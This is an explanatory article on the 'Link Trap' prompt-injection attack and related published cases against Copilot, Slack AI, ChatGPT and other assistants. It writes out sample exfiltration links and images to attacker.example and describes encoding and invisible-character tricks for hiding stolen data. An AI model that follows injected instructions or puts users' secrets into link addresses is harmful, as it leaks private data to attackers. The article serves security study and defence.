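# Link Trap: prompt injection that hides user data in a link

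## How the Link Trap attack works

Link Trap is an attack on AI assistants. An attacker plants text that makes the assistant put a user's private information into the address of a web link, and the attacker receives the information when the user clicks the link. The name comes from *Link Trap*, a short article that the security company Trend Micro published in December 2024.

Link Trap is a form of prompt injection, in which text gets a language model to follow an attacker's instructions instead of, or as well as, the user's. Many prompt injections do damage through the assistant's tools, for example by making it send an email or change a database. In a Link Trap, the assistant only writes an answer containing a link with the user's data hidden in it, and the user's browser sends the data when the user clicks the link. The unauthorised transfer of data to an outside party is called exfiltration,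 and it is a one-click leak when it happens because the user clicks a link the assistant wrote.

### Instructions and data in one stream

A language model, the program behind assistants such as ChatGPT, produces text by predicting the next token (a word or part of one) from the text before it. The software around the model joins the request, chat history, retrieved documents and stored memories into a single sequence called the context, which is all the text the model has when it answers.

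David C compares prompt injection with SQL injection in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. In SQL injection, which attackers used for decades, they type database commands into web forms and get the database to run them. Developers can now prevent this because a database engine can keep commands separate from what visitors enter. A language model has no such separation and only predicts the next token from all the text it receives. David C therefore thinks it very possible that nobody will ever stop prompt injection as completely as developers can stop SQL injection.

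Developers use tags to mark which text comes from the user, which from the model and which from a tool, such as one that fetched a web page. They intend the model to use fetched text as information but never to follow instructions in it. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) studied how these tags affect a model's internal activity. They wrapped identical passages in different tags and trained simple classifiers on that activity, so the classifiers could learn only the effect of the tags. When the researchers then put text in a user's style inside a tool's tags, the classifiers mostly identified it as user text, so style had outweighed the tags. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent give up data, the attack succeeded 2% of the time where this confusion was lowest and 70% of the time where it was highest.

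*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in models that map instructions and data into the same internal space, unless the architecture enforces a separation. The proof doesn't show how often any given attack works. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the attacks the company sees against ChatGPT mostly try to send secrets from a conversation to a third party, and that most of them fail because the model has been trained to refuse. One attack that outside researchers reported in 2025 still worked in half of the tests.

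An attacker can put the injected text in material that the assistant reads, such as an email, a document or a web page. This is called indirect prompt injection, and the attacker doesn't need access to the assistant. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides an instruction in a CV for the recruiter's AI system to approve the candidate.

The user can also paste in the malicious prompt. Keysight's *Understanding The Link Trap Prompt Injection Attack*, a June 2025 post by a maker of network test equipment, lists help forums, a tip in a work chat, and collections of "useful" prompts on the code-sharing site GitHub as likely sources. A chat interface may record which words the user pasted, but the model usually receives the whole message as one block, so it can mistake the user's own words for pasted text. In *Can LLMs Separate Pasted Artifacts from User Speech?*, Panthi, Yeamin and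 Abdelfattah (2026) gave 20 models 300 editing tasks in which a casual remark from the user followed the pasted text on the next line. Every model sometimes worked the remark into the edited text, at rates from 7.7% to 66.7%. Claude Opus 4.8 did so in 19% of cases and GPT-5.6-sol in 32%. Explicit markers around the paste lowered those two rates to 2% and 11.7%.

The experiment had no attacker, and the models mistook the user's words for part of the pasted text, which is the reverse of what happens in an injection. Still, it shows that models often fail to tell the two apart when nothing marks the boundary. Markers would help less when a user pastes in a whole prompt because a stranger recommended it. That user wants the model to follow the pasted text but hasn't noticed all the instructions in it.

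### How a link carries data out

Chat assistants commonly format their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation. A Markdown link puts the visible words in square brackets and the address in round ones:

`[reference](https://attacker.example/note?d=QW5u)`

The chat window displays this as one clickable word, "reference". The address stays hidden unless the user hovers over the link or copies it.

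In that address, `attacker.example` is the server and `/note` is a page on it. Everything after the question mark is the query string, which ordinary websites use for things like search terms. When the user clicks the link, the browser sends the query string to the server with its request for the page. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that visiting a link also sends the website the full address, which websites commonly log.

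Web servers routinely log such requests. According to Apache's *Log Files*, documentation for an older version of a widely used web server, the access log records every request the server processes. A typical entry includes the visitor's IP address, the time, and the request line with its query string. For the link above, the entry would contain something like `GET /note?d=QW5u HTTP/1.1`. An attacker who runs the server only has to open the log file. The page doesn't need to exist, because the server also logs requests that end in "not found".

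HTTPS, the encrypted form of web traffic, does not protect the data from the attacker. It hides the query string from eavesdroppers on the network, but the attacker's server receives the request and decrypts it. *Information exposure through query strings in url*, from OWASP, a non-profit that catalogues software flaws, lists other places where the data can appear even over HTTPS, including the browser's history, its cache and the header that tells a website which page a visitor came from.

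An assistant can put personal data in a link even when no attacker is involved. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a user who asks where to find cars for sale nearby. ChatGPT already has the user's city from the conversation, so it may link to a car-search page whose address ends in "London". The link is useful, but clicking it reveals to the car site where the user lives. Smuggled data usually goes in the query string, after the question mark, but it can also go in the path, as the city does here.

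### Trend Micro's account

Trend Micro describes the attack in two steps. In the first, the assistant receives a prompt that contains both the user's question and the attacker's instructions to collect sensitive information and append it to an address the attacker supplies. The attacker may also instruct the assistant to hide the full address behind an innocuous word, such as "reference".

In the second step, the model gives an answer that is mostly what the user wanted. Someone who asked about Japan, for example, gets accurate information about Japan. The link comes at the end, where a reader would expect a source. If the user clicks it, the data goes to the attacker.

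The amount of data an attacker can steal depends on the assistant. With a public chatbot, the injected text would target the chat history, including any personal details, plans and schedules the user has typed. With a company's private assistant, it could instruct the assistant to search all the reference material the company has supplied, including internal passwords and confidential documents. The company case is more serious because more data is exposed and because an employee who clicks the link can leak documents they have never opened, whereas a chatbot user would leak data they had typed themselves.

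The article describes a possible attack and does not report a test of it. It presents the technique as new and says researchers had recently "begun discussing" it, but it names no researchers or vulnerable product and gives no success rate. The technique was also less new than the article suggests. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes the same Markdown-link leak as familiar from "a dozen different products already".

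Jay Liao wrote the article, according to the byline on the Japanese version, Trend Micro's *生成AIプロンプトインジェクションの新たな手口「リンクトラップ」*. A conference profile from April 2025, iThome's *Jay Liao*, lists Liao as a senior technical manager in Trend Micro's AI Lab who has recently worked on engines that detect attacks on AI. The article ends with advice to inspect prompts and be wary of links, followed by a pitch for a Trend Micro product that filters both prompts and answers. This doesn't make the mechanism wrong, but evidence that the attack works has to come from elsewhere.

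### Keysight's worked example

Keysight gives an example with details that Trend Micro left out. A user called Annie tells a chatbot that she is going to San Diego the next day to collect her Mastercard, and types the card number. Later the chatbot receives a prompt that asks for a few North American desserts and a link with the text "reference", whose address should end in a base64-encoded summary of the earlier chat. The chatbot's answer lists cheesecake, apple pie and brownies, followed by the link.

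Base64 is a way to write any data in 64 ordinary characters. *The Base16, Base32, and Base64 Data Encodings* (Josefsson, 2006) describes the standard method, which takes three bytes (24 bits) at a time, splits them into four groups of six bits, and looks up a character for each group. For example, the three bytes of "Ann" form groups with the values 16, 22, 57 and 46, which stand for Q, W, 5 and u, so "Ann" becomes `QW5u`. Anyone can decode the text by reversing the lookup. Josefsson warns that Base64 provides no confidentiality, but it does hide a password from a casual glance, which is enough for a Link Trap.

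Base64 writes every three bytes as four characters, so *n* bytes take up 4 × ⌈*n*/3⌉ characters, where the brackets mean rounding up. Keysight's string encodes 115 bytes, which makes 39 groups, or 156 characters, the last two of them equals signs that pad out the final group. Encoding makes the data about a third longer, but the link hides the extra length from the user. A 600-byte summary becomes 800 characters of address behind the same single word. Standard base64 also uses the plus sign and the slash, which can cause trouble in web addresses, and Josefsson defines a variant that replaces them; Keysight's string contains neither.

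When its printed lines are joined, the string decodes to a greeting ("Hello Annie! Hi my name as Annie"), followed by the San Diego errand and the card number. The decoded text differs slightly from what Annie typed. Her card number began with 4352, but the decoded one begins with 3452, and an invisible control character (ASCII 6) appears where there should be a space before "going".

The control character appears because one letter is in the wrong case. The string has `IG0G`, and `IG0g` would have produced the space. The swapped digits change three base64 characters in a row, and all three are correct for the wrong number, which looks more like a number miscopied before encoding than an encoding error. The address also doesn't match, since the prompt asks for the path `/chat` and the answer has `/leak`.

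Keysight may well have composed the answer as an illustration, but a model could also have made such mistakes. *Base64Bench*, a small benchmark from October 2025, had models encode and decode strings without tools or written-out reasoning. The best model, Claude 3.7 Sonnet, was perfect 75.9% of the time. It encoded only 42% of random strings of about 130 characters without error, whereas all but the smallest models did well on common words. These are 2025 models, and an assistant that can run code doesn't need to encode the text itself. If a model does make such errors, a thief could still understand travel plans with a wrong character or two, but couldn't use a card number or password with the same errors. Card numbers and passwords are also closer to the random strings on which the models did worst.

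The link is useful to an attacker only if the injected text enters the victim's context and the answer appears in front of the victim. Keysight's post suggests that an attacker could submit the prompt directly to a public chatbot that retains past conversations, but this wouldn't work as described because the chatbot would return the answer, including the link, to the attacker. An attacker already in Annie's session wouldn't need the link, since they could ask for her history and read it on the screen, and one in a separate session couldn't access her history unless the chatbot mixed up its users.

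Keysight wrote the post to introduce additions to its test products. It added seven simulated attacks to BreakingPoint, a tool that generates network traffic. The attacks cover data such as bank details, health records and government identity numbers. Keysight says it could not replicate real sessions exactly, so each simulation puts the chat history into the request and then simulates the answer that leaks the data. Keysight planned to add 18 more simulations, aimed at models from OpenAI, Google and xAI, to a second product, CyPerf. CyPerf's statistics show whether a security device on the network let the request and the response through, so customers can check whether a filter catches Link Trap traffic. The post gives no figure for how often a real model complies.

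### Whether the attack needs permissions

Trend Micro's main argument is that Link Trap can work even if the AI has no power to send email, place orders or call outside services, because it leaves the upload to the user, "who inherently has higher permissions". The company says such an assistant is commonly considered fairly safe, on the belief that prompt injection can do only as much harm as the AI's permissions allow. Keysight goes further and writes that the technique works "without any explicit permissions or plugin access".

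The attack doesn't require outward-facing tools, because an assistant with no connection to the outside world can still write a link. But the assistant must have private data in its context or within its reach, it must take in the attacker's text, and its chat window must display clickable links. In a fresh chat with no memory or documents, there would be nothing worth collecting. If the chat window showed addresses as plain text, the user would see a long string of gibberish and would have to copy it into a browser by hand for the attack to work.

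*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) gives nearly the same list: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. Willison warns that an attacker can steal the private data from any system that has all three. Trend Micro's case includes the third element, though this may not be obvious at first, because Willison's examples of external communication include "providing a link for a user to click". OpenAI similarly divides the parts into a source, through which the attacker influences the system, and a sink, where a capability becomes dangerous. It counts following a link as a sink.

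The disagreement is over what counts as a permission. Willison's count is more useful to anyone building an assistant, because it treats displaying links as a capability that somebody chose to turn on and could restrict. The same is true of access to private data. In Trend Micro's company example, the assistant can search internal documents and passwords only because somebody at the company gave it that access.

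## Assistants that were made to leak data through clickable links

Between 2023 and 2026, researchers got several widely used assistants to write links that would leak private data when clicked. They reported most of these flaws to the vendors before publishing, so the cases also show how the vendors reacted.

### Bing Chat and Microsoft 365 Copilot

In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) tried an early version of the idea on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, which could run in a sidebar of the Edge browser and read the page the user had open. They put instructions in an HTML comment, which browsers don't display, telling Bing Chat to persuade the user to reveal their real name. They had in mind a government trying to identify journalists or whistle-blowers.

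In one session, a researcher posed as a journalist and gave the name John Smith. Bing Chat then offered a link to an exclusive website, with an access code made from the name. The code was `htimSnhJo`, which is "John Smith" backwards with the last two letters swapped. It came after a hash mark in the address. Browsers don't send that part to the server, so the attacker would have needed a script on the page to read the code or the user to type it in. Greshake and colleagues also noted that Bing Chat could disguise a suspicious address with a Markdown link.

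Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, could already read the user's emails and documents, so an attacker didn't need it to persuade the user to supply private data, as Bing Chat had to. In early 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger built an attack on Copilot, which he describes in *Microsoft Copilot* on his blog, Embrace The Red. He planted instructions in an email or a shared document. When the user asked Copilot about that item, Copilot followed the instructions, searched for other emails without asking the user, and put their contents into a link. In the demonstrations the link contained sales figures and one-time codes for logging in to Slack.

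Rehberger hid the data with a trick called ASCII smuggling. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes a set of "tag" characters that mirror the ordinary letters, digits and punctuation marks. Each tag's number is 917,504 higher than that of its ordinary character, so "h" is 104 and its tag is 917,608. Tags are invisible on most web pages. Copilot could therefore add a whole email, written in tags, to the end of a short web address, and the user would see only the short address. Rehberger's injected text included the phrase "hello, today is a good day" written in tags, as an example to teach Copilot the method.

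The disguise is imperfect because a browser rewrites each invisible tag character as twelve ordinary ones (`%F3%A0%81%A8` for "h") before sending the request, which makes the real address far longer than the one on the screen. Rehberger invites readers to hover over a sample link and see that something looks wrong.

An attacker could also target one person, because Copilot has access to the user's name, job title and manager's name. In *Trust No AI*, a survey of his own findings, Rehberger (2024) describes injected instructions that take effect only when a particular user, such as the chief executive, opens the email.

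Rehberger reported the invisible characters to Microsoft on 17 January 2024, and Microsoft closed the report the next day as low severity. It opened a case in February after he sent the full attack. By early July the attack no longer worked, and Rehberger presented it at a conference in August. Microsoft did not answer when he asked what it had changed, but Copilot seemed to have stopped displaying links. After a similar report, Amazon also stopped displaying links in Amazon Q for Business, its workplace assistant.

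### Slack AI

The clearest case is in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, which the security company PromptArmor published in August 2024. Slack is a workplace chat service that sorts messages into channels. Every member of a workspace can read its public channels, but only invited members can read a private one. Slack AI answers questions by retrieving relevant messages and giving them to a language model. It searches the user's private channels and all public ones, including those the user has never joined.

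In PromptArmor's demonstration, a developer has saved an API key (a secret code that lets a program use an online service) in a private channel with no other members. The attacker has an account in the same workspace but can't read that channel. The attacker creates a public channel, also with no other members, and posts one message in it.

The message starts with the name of the API key so that a search for the key will find the message. The rest is the answer the attacker wants Slack AI to give, an error notice followed by a link that reads "click here to reauthenticate". The link goes to the attacker's server, and its query string contains a placeholder word. In the message, the attacker tells Slack AI to replace that word with the real key, which the attacker has never seen.

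Later the developer asks Slack AI for the key. The search finds both the developer's private note and the attacker's message and puts them in the same context for the model. The model answers with the error notice and the link, whose address is now `https://attacker.example/?secret=` followed by the real key. If the developer clicks the link, expecting to log in again, the browser sends the key to the attacker.

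Slack AI is supposed to cite every message that contributed to an answer, but it cited only the developer's note, not the attacker's message that supplied the link. That message didn't appear on the first page of search results either. In a second test, PromptArmor had Slack AI show an ordinary phishing link to a user who asked about a manager's messages, and this time Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel. Users therefore couldn't rely on the citations to expose the attack.

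PromptArmor stresses that the attacker doesn't need to know what secrets people have stored, but in the demonstration the attacker knew the name of the service and had to wait for somebody to ask about it. The same search also turned up other messages about API keys, so PromptArmor suspected that an attacker could steal other secrets without naming them, but it didn't demonstrate this. On 14 August 2024 Slack AI began to read uploaded files as well as messages. PromptArmor considered it highly likely that an attacker with no Slack account could then have succeeded if an employee uploaded a PDF with hidden instructions, but it didn't test this.

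PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack that same day. On 19 August Slack replied that the evidence was insufficient. It said that the information in PromptArmor's first video was in a public channel, which every member of a workspace can read, and called this "intended behavior." The attacker's message was in a public channel, but in the attack PromptArmor described, the key was in a private one. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem.

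PromptArmor published its findings on 20 August, and Slack deployed a patch the same day. The next day, Slack (2024) announced that it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. In a statement quoted in ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*, Slack described the flaw as a way for one user to trick another with a phishing link "under very limited circumstances". The attacker did need an account in the workspace, but "phishing" makes the attack sound easier to resist than it was. Unlike a phishing victim, the user didn't have to type in the secret, because the link already contained it. Slack did not explain in either statement what the patch changed.

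### Later variants

Before Trend Micro named the attack, Microsoft and Slack had both fixed flaws that allowed working versions of it. The technique is at least a year and a half older than its name, counting from the work of Greshake and colleagues, and researchers have kept finding new ways to show users such links.

In August 2025 the security researcher Adam Logue reported a second attack of this kind on Microsoft 365 Copilot. BeyondMachines' *Microsoft 365 Copilot vulnerability enables data theft through malicious Mermaid diagrams* (2025) describes the attack. Logue prepared an Excel file with ordinary-looking financial data on the first sheet and instructions in white text on both sheets. When a user asked for a summary, the instructions diverted Copilot from that task in stages. Copilot used its email search tool to fetch the user's recent emails, and told the user that the document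 was sensitive and required a login to view.

The login button was a diagram that Copilot drew from Mermaid, a notation that describes flowcharts in text and allows styling and clickable links. Logue's instructions made the diagram look like a button with a padlock and put the emails in the link's address. Copilot encoded the emails in hexadecimal, which writes each byte as two characters, so "Meeting" becomes `4d656574696e67`. Mermaid accepted at most 200 characters on a line, so Logue had Copilot split the encoded string into lines of no more than 30 characters, or 15 bytes of email.

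After a click, the button turned into a small frame that displayed whatever the attacker's server sent. Logue sent a picture of Microsoft's real login screen, so the user saw roughly what they expected. The frame disappeared from the chat a few seconds later, leaving little to inspect.

According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, Microsoft had trouble reproducing the attack until Logue sent videos. It confirmed the flaw on 8 September and had fixed it by 26 September by removing clickable links from the diagrams. Logue received no reward because Copilot was outside the scope of Microsoft's bounty programme. If Rehberger was right that Copilot had stopped displaying ordinary links in 2024, the diagram feature had brought links back. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a similar problem with a feature added later, a preview for web pages, which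 could leak data without a click until Microsoft fixed it in March 2026.

Lian, Wang and colleagues (2025) used a much simpler link in *Prompt-in-Content Attacks*. They uploaded Word documents to seven assistants through the assistants' normal web pages and asked for a summary. Each document had one of four instructions in the middle of harmless text: refuse the task, output an unrelated sentence, send the user to a given website, or disparage the document.

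| Assistant | Instructions followed, out of four |
|---|---|
| Grok 3 | 4 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 4 |
| Kimi | 4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 2 |
| Perplexity | 1 |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 0 |
| ChatGPT 4o | 0 |

None of these four instructions involved private data. In an exploratory test, the researchers then changed the third one so that the assistant had to look for passwords or other secrets earlier in the conversation and add them to the address. They show the result only for Grok 3. The user had mentioned that a database password was 12345678, and Grok had advised changing it. After the upload, Grok recommended visiting an address that ended in "Database access password" and the password itself, in plain text. A screenshot shows the same text under "Query strings", apparently as a server received it.

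This is weak evidence about assistants in general. The attack succeeded once, with a model xAI has since replaced, and Lian and colleagues don't report how many times they tried it. They also noticed that Kimi's answers varied between identical tests, so one run is a poor measure of how often an attack works. Four of the seven assistants followed an instruction in the document to pass on a fixed link, but the researchers don't show whether the other three of those four would also have put a password in it. The password was also readable in the address, so an attentive user might well have noticed it.

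The security company Radware reported a different kind of link in January 2026. Radware's *The AI Is the Phisher*, published by September 2026, describes two attacks on Microsoft Copilot and ChatGPT. In both, the instructions were in a shared document or an email that the assistant read for the user.

In what Radware calls the one-click variant, the user asks for help with a finance report. The assistant collects unrelated personal information from its saved memories and from connected services such as the Outlook mailbox. Radware's demonstrations exposed a user's name, home address and phone number, and the times they usually visited a café and came home. The assistant then writes a small web page in HTML that contains this information, encoded in base64. It gives the user a link with the message "Your answer is ready here."

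Clicking that link only downloads the file. When the user opens the file, the page sends a request containing the encoded information to the attacker's server. "One-click" is therefore slightly inaccurate, since the user has to both click the link and open the file. The variant also differs from a Link Trap in the strict sense because the private data is in the file, not in the address the user clicks, so inspecting the link's query string would reveal nothing suspicious.

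Radware's other variant uses a phishing page tailored to the user's request to collect information that the assistant doesn't have. A user who asked for cheap headphones on Amazon received a file that looked like an Amazon checkout page. The file sent the attacker any card details and password the user typed in. eWeek's *'ChatGPhish' Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* describes a related attack, in which hidden instructions on a web page can make ChatGPT's summary display the attacker's links.

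Microsoft passed Radware's report to the product team. OpenAI's bug-reporting programme, which Bugcrowd runs, classified the report as "Not Applicable" on 4 February 2026. According to Bugcrowd, OpenAI thought Radware had not shown how the attack differed from any other case in which someone persuades a victim to open a malicious file. Radware answered that in this attack the victim starts the conversation, is waiting for an answer, and gets the link from a system they already trust, which can also tailor the lure to the task. Radware received no further reply.

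OpenAI was right that the last step requires the user to open a downloaded file. According to its post, Radware responded mainly by explaining why people would fall for the link. A stronger reply is that this file, unlike an ordinary malicious one, already contained the victim's home address when it arrived, because the assistant had collected the address and written it there. When Radware later repeated its tests, the attack no longer worked on either product. Radware infers that both companies had blocked the specific routes it used.

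### How the assistants got the private data

The demonstrations differ in how much the assistant had to do for the attacker. Bing Chat and Grok 3 used only what the user had typed in the same conversation. Slack AI had to search, but the developer's own question triggered the search, and Slack AI would have run it the same way without an attacker.

In Rehberger's and Logue's attacks on Copilot, the injected instructions made the assistant call a search tool to find emails that the user hadn't asked about. Radware's case falls between attacks that leak data already in the assistant's context and attacks that make the assistant look data up. Saved memories may already be in the context, but the assistant would have to look up anything in the mailbox, and Radware doesn't say which details came from which source.

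Trend Micro's argument that an assistant can leak data without extra permissions therefore fits Slack AI and Grok 3 better than Copilot. If Copilot had needed the user's approval before searching the mailbox again, a careful user could have stopped both attacks before any email reached the link. The same rule would not have protected the developer on Slack, who wanted the search. Copilot's search tool also let Rehberger target specific data, such as login codes, whereas PromptArmor's attacker had to wait until someone asked for the key.

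### Use by real attackers

All of these cases are demonstrations by researchers, and none of the researchers or vendors reports data theft by this method. The OECD's incident monitor classifies the Slack flaw as a plausible future harm, not an actual incident, in its entry *Slack AI Vulnerability Exposes Private Channel Data*. The entry's text is AI-generated.

Two searches of the public web found very little that resembles Link Trap. Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses and, with two further sources, confirmed 15,387 injections. Only 13 were attempts to extract data. Nine of these targeted the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions to the model) and four targeted secrets. A template found on 359 pages of a single host contained an instruction to send the user to a particular website, but it had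 no place for the user's data.

Google reported a similar search in April 2026. It found a small number of injections aimed at stealing data, and its example was a website author's experiment. It did not see significant use of the more advanced prompts that researchers had published in 2025. SecurityWeek's *Malicious AI Prompt Injection Attacks Increasing, but Sophistication Still Low* reports that some of the injections instructed an AI to collect credentials and send them to an email address, rather than through a link that the user clicks. Google found 32% more malicious injections in February 2026 than in November 2025, and expects their number and sophistication to grow.

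Neither search could have found the attacks on Copilot or Slack, because web crawlers don't reach private emails, shared spreadsheets or workplace channels. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reported in October 2026 that the security company Barracuda had found phishing emails with hidden instructions for AI assistants. Such emails could deliver a Link Trap, but Barracuda's finding doesn't show that anyone has stolen data through a link.

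A successful theft would also be hard to notice. The victim sees an ordinary answer, clicks a link and perhaps gets an error page. Slack AI's citation left out the attacker's message, and Logue's button removed itself from the chat. The only complete record of the stolen data is the log on the attacker's server, so the lack of known victims is only weak evidence that there have been none.

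## What the click changes: comparison with leaks that need none

A zero-click leak can use the same address as a Link Trap, but software requests it without waiting for the user. If the assistant writes the earlier example, `https://attacker.example/note?d=QW5u`, as a link, the user's browser requests it after a click. The same browser requests it as soon as the answer appears if the assistant writes it as an image. In a messaging app, the app company's server may request it to build a preview, and an agent that can open web pages may request it before writing any answer. The attacker's log contains the same query string each time, though the request may come from a different computer or at a different time.

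### Images that load by themselves

A Markdown image is a Markdown link with an exclamation mark in front:

`![reference](https://attacker.example/note?d=QW5u)`

A chat window that supports images tries to load a picture from that address. As Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* explains, the browser then connects to the server without any action by the user.

The software engineer Roman Samoilenko demonstrated this on ChatGPT in April 2023. His *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes a web page with a script that adds hidden instructions to any text a visitor copies. When the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, the instructions make ChatGPT end its answer with a transparent image, one pixel wide, whose address contains data from the chat. In one test, the data was code that ChatGPT had just corrected, including a password. Samoilenko also got ChatGPT to add such an image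 to every later answer, so the server received each new message the user typed.

Another of Samoilenko's examples is a Link Trap, although it isn't called one. ChatGPT puts the corrected code in the query string of an ordinary link, and the site's owner receives the code if the user clicks.

Results varied between attempts. ChatGPT readily added earlier prompts or code to the address, but Samoilenko found it very difficult to make it add passwords or API keys on request. OpenAI began to mitigate the image leak only in December 2023, according to Willison (2023). In May 2026, the security company Permiso reported in *ChatGPhish* that ChatGPT still loaded images from a web page it had summarised. Loading them revealed the user's IP address and the time of the answer, but Permiso did not show chat data leaking this way.

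EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, began as a one-click leak, and its discoverers then removed the click. Aim Security reported it to Microsoft in January 2025, and *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes it step by step. The attacker emails an employee instructions that seem meant for the employee, which gets them past Microsoft's filter for prompt injection. Willison adds that the email covered several likely topics, such as staff leave, so that Copilot would retrieve it for many different questions. When the employee asks one of these, Copilot picks out the most sensitive information in its context and puts it in a web address.

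Microsoft had programmed Copilot to remove external links from its answers, which fits Rehberger's impression in 2024 that links had disappeared. But the filter recognised only the usual Markdown notation and missed links that give the address on a separate line. At this stage EchoLeak was a Link Trap, with a secret hidden in a link behind clickable text.

Aim Security then turned the link into an image, using the same alternative notation. The browser still refused to load images from unknown sites, so the researchers routed the request through a Microsoft Teams address the browser was allowed to contact. Reddy and Gujral write that the attacker's log would show either a Microsoft server or the victim's own IP address. The employee still had to ask Copilot a question, so "zero-click" means only that nobody had to click the result.

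Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025 and said it had no evidence that anyone had exploited it. Rehberger and PromptArmor had both demonstrated leaks from commercial products in 2024, so Reddy and Gujral overstate when they call EchoLeak the first known case of prompt injection causing concrete data exfiltration from a production system.

### Link previews and agents

Slack, Telegram and similar apps fetch the links in a message to show a title and a picture. In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* described how, when an AI agent posts a link with private data in it, the app's preview request delivers that data to the attacker without a click. PromptArmor found that this worked by default with OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can message through Telegram. Turning off previews in OpenClaw's Telegram settings stopped the automatic leak, but the user can still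 click the link.

PromptArmor also set up a public page where people could test their own agents and report the results. *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* (Apostol) lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, and Slack with certain bots, among the exposed combinations. Because volunteers reported these results, they show that a combination can leak but not how often. The risk was known earlier than PromptArmor's phrase "largely unrecognized" suggests. In August 2024, Willison (2024) passed on Rehberger's advice in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* that apps posting to Slack can turn off previews for their own messages.

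An agent that can open web addresses can leak data without showing the user a link. It can send the request from the computer it runs on or from its provider's servers, as in Radware's *ZombieAgent*, where the data left through OpenAI's servers. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) measured how often an agent could be made to leak data this way. They put a secret in the context of an agent built on the small model qwen2.5:7b, gave it a tool for making web requests, and asked it to summarise a web page that contained instructions to send the secret to their server.

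The researchers put the instructions in the page's title, its description, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and had to send the secret whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The agent contacted the server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1% (the paper's abstract gives about 89%). This included 238 of the 240 runs with a whole secret and 185 of the 240 with a divided one. It never contacted the server in 120 further runs with harmless pages. The summary looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks, so a check on the answer text would have missed them. A Link Trap can't avoid such a check by keeping the address out of the answer, because the user has to click it there.

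Lan and colleagues then tried several defences on one of the simplest attacks, with 30 runs for each.

| Defence | Agent tried to send data | Data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| List of permitted domains | 100% | 0% |
| Block on suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
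| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking strings | 0% | 0% |

Telling the model to ignore instructions from the web helped only somewhat, while every control on the requests prevented the leak. The evidence is strongest for the list of permitted domains, since the agent tried to send the secret every time and failed every time. The block on suspicious addresses had an easier test, because it rejected any path containing the word "collect" and the researchers' server used the path `/collect`. The filter for random-looking strings never had anything to block. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids such strings when the filter is active, but they don't explain how information about the filter would reach the model.

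Lan and colleagues obtained the 88% figure in a test that favoured the attacker, with a single small model and almost no system prompt, so it is not an estimate for commercial assistants. OpenAI reports that most such attacks on ChatGPT fail. The domain list's success doesn't carry over to Link Trap, because the list controls only the agent's requests, not those of the user's browser.

### How many people would click

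An attack that needs a click fails when the user ignores the link. Pew Research Center's *Google users are less likely to click on links* (2025) gives an idea of how often that might happen. Pew tracked the web browsing of 900 US adults in March 2025, including 12,593 Google searches that produced an AI summary. Users clicked a link in the summary in 1% of visits to those pages. They clicked an ordinary search result in 8% of those visits, compared with 15% when there was no summary.

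Pew measured clicks on ordinary citations rather than injected links, so the 1% figure is not a success rate for Link Trap. The figure is most relevant to Trend Micro's version, in which a link called "reference" follows a complete answer and the user has little reason to click. More people would probably click the login link in PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI, because they would think they had to log in to get the key, but PromptArmor didn't measure how many.

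If users clicked injected links at the 1% rate Pew found for citations, 1,000 answers containing one would bring the attacker about ten clicks. An image that loaded automatically would send data from all 1,000. An attacker could improve the odds with a lasting instruction like Samoilenko's, which adds the link to every answer. The chance of at least one click in 50 answers would then be 1 − 0.99⁵⁰, or roughly 40%. This overestimates the attacker's chances because it treats each answer as independent, when someone who has ignored ten such links will probably ignore the next.

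The advantage for the attacker is that a link still works when the developer blocks images. A chat assistant can do without images from unknown websites much more easily than without links, which users need to check sources.

### Whether a one-click leak is a vulnerability

Google's Gemini, for example, blocks external images but displays links. *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the security company Checkmarx, reports that an attacker could still use those links to leak data. Google removes links that its Safe Browsing service has already flagged as malicious, but an attacker can register a new domain.

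Checkmarx reported this to Google on 5 October 2025, and Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Google said the issue was not severe enough to track as a security bug, and that its reward programme covers only flaws that "substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data".

Google gave two separate reasons, and a problem that is infeasible to fix may still be severe. Checkmarx accepted "infeasible" as an answer, but argued that users should get a warning because Google's position leaves them to manage the risk. That seems right, since few users would guess that a link in Gemini's answer could contain their data.

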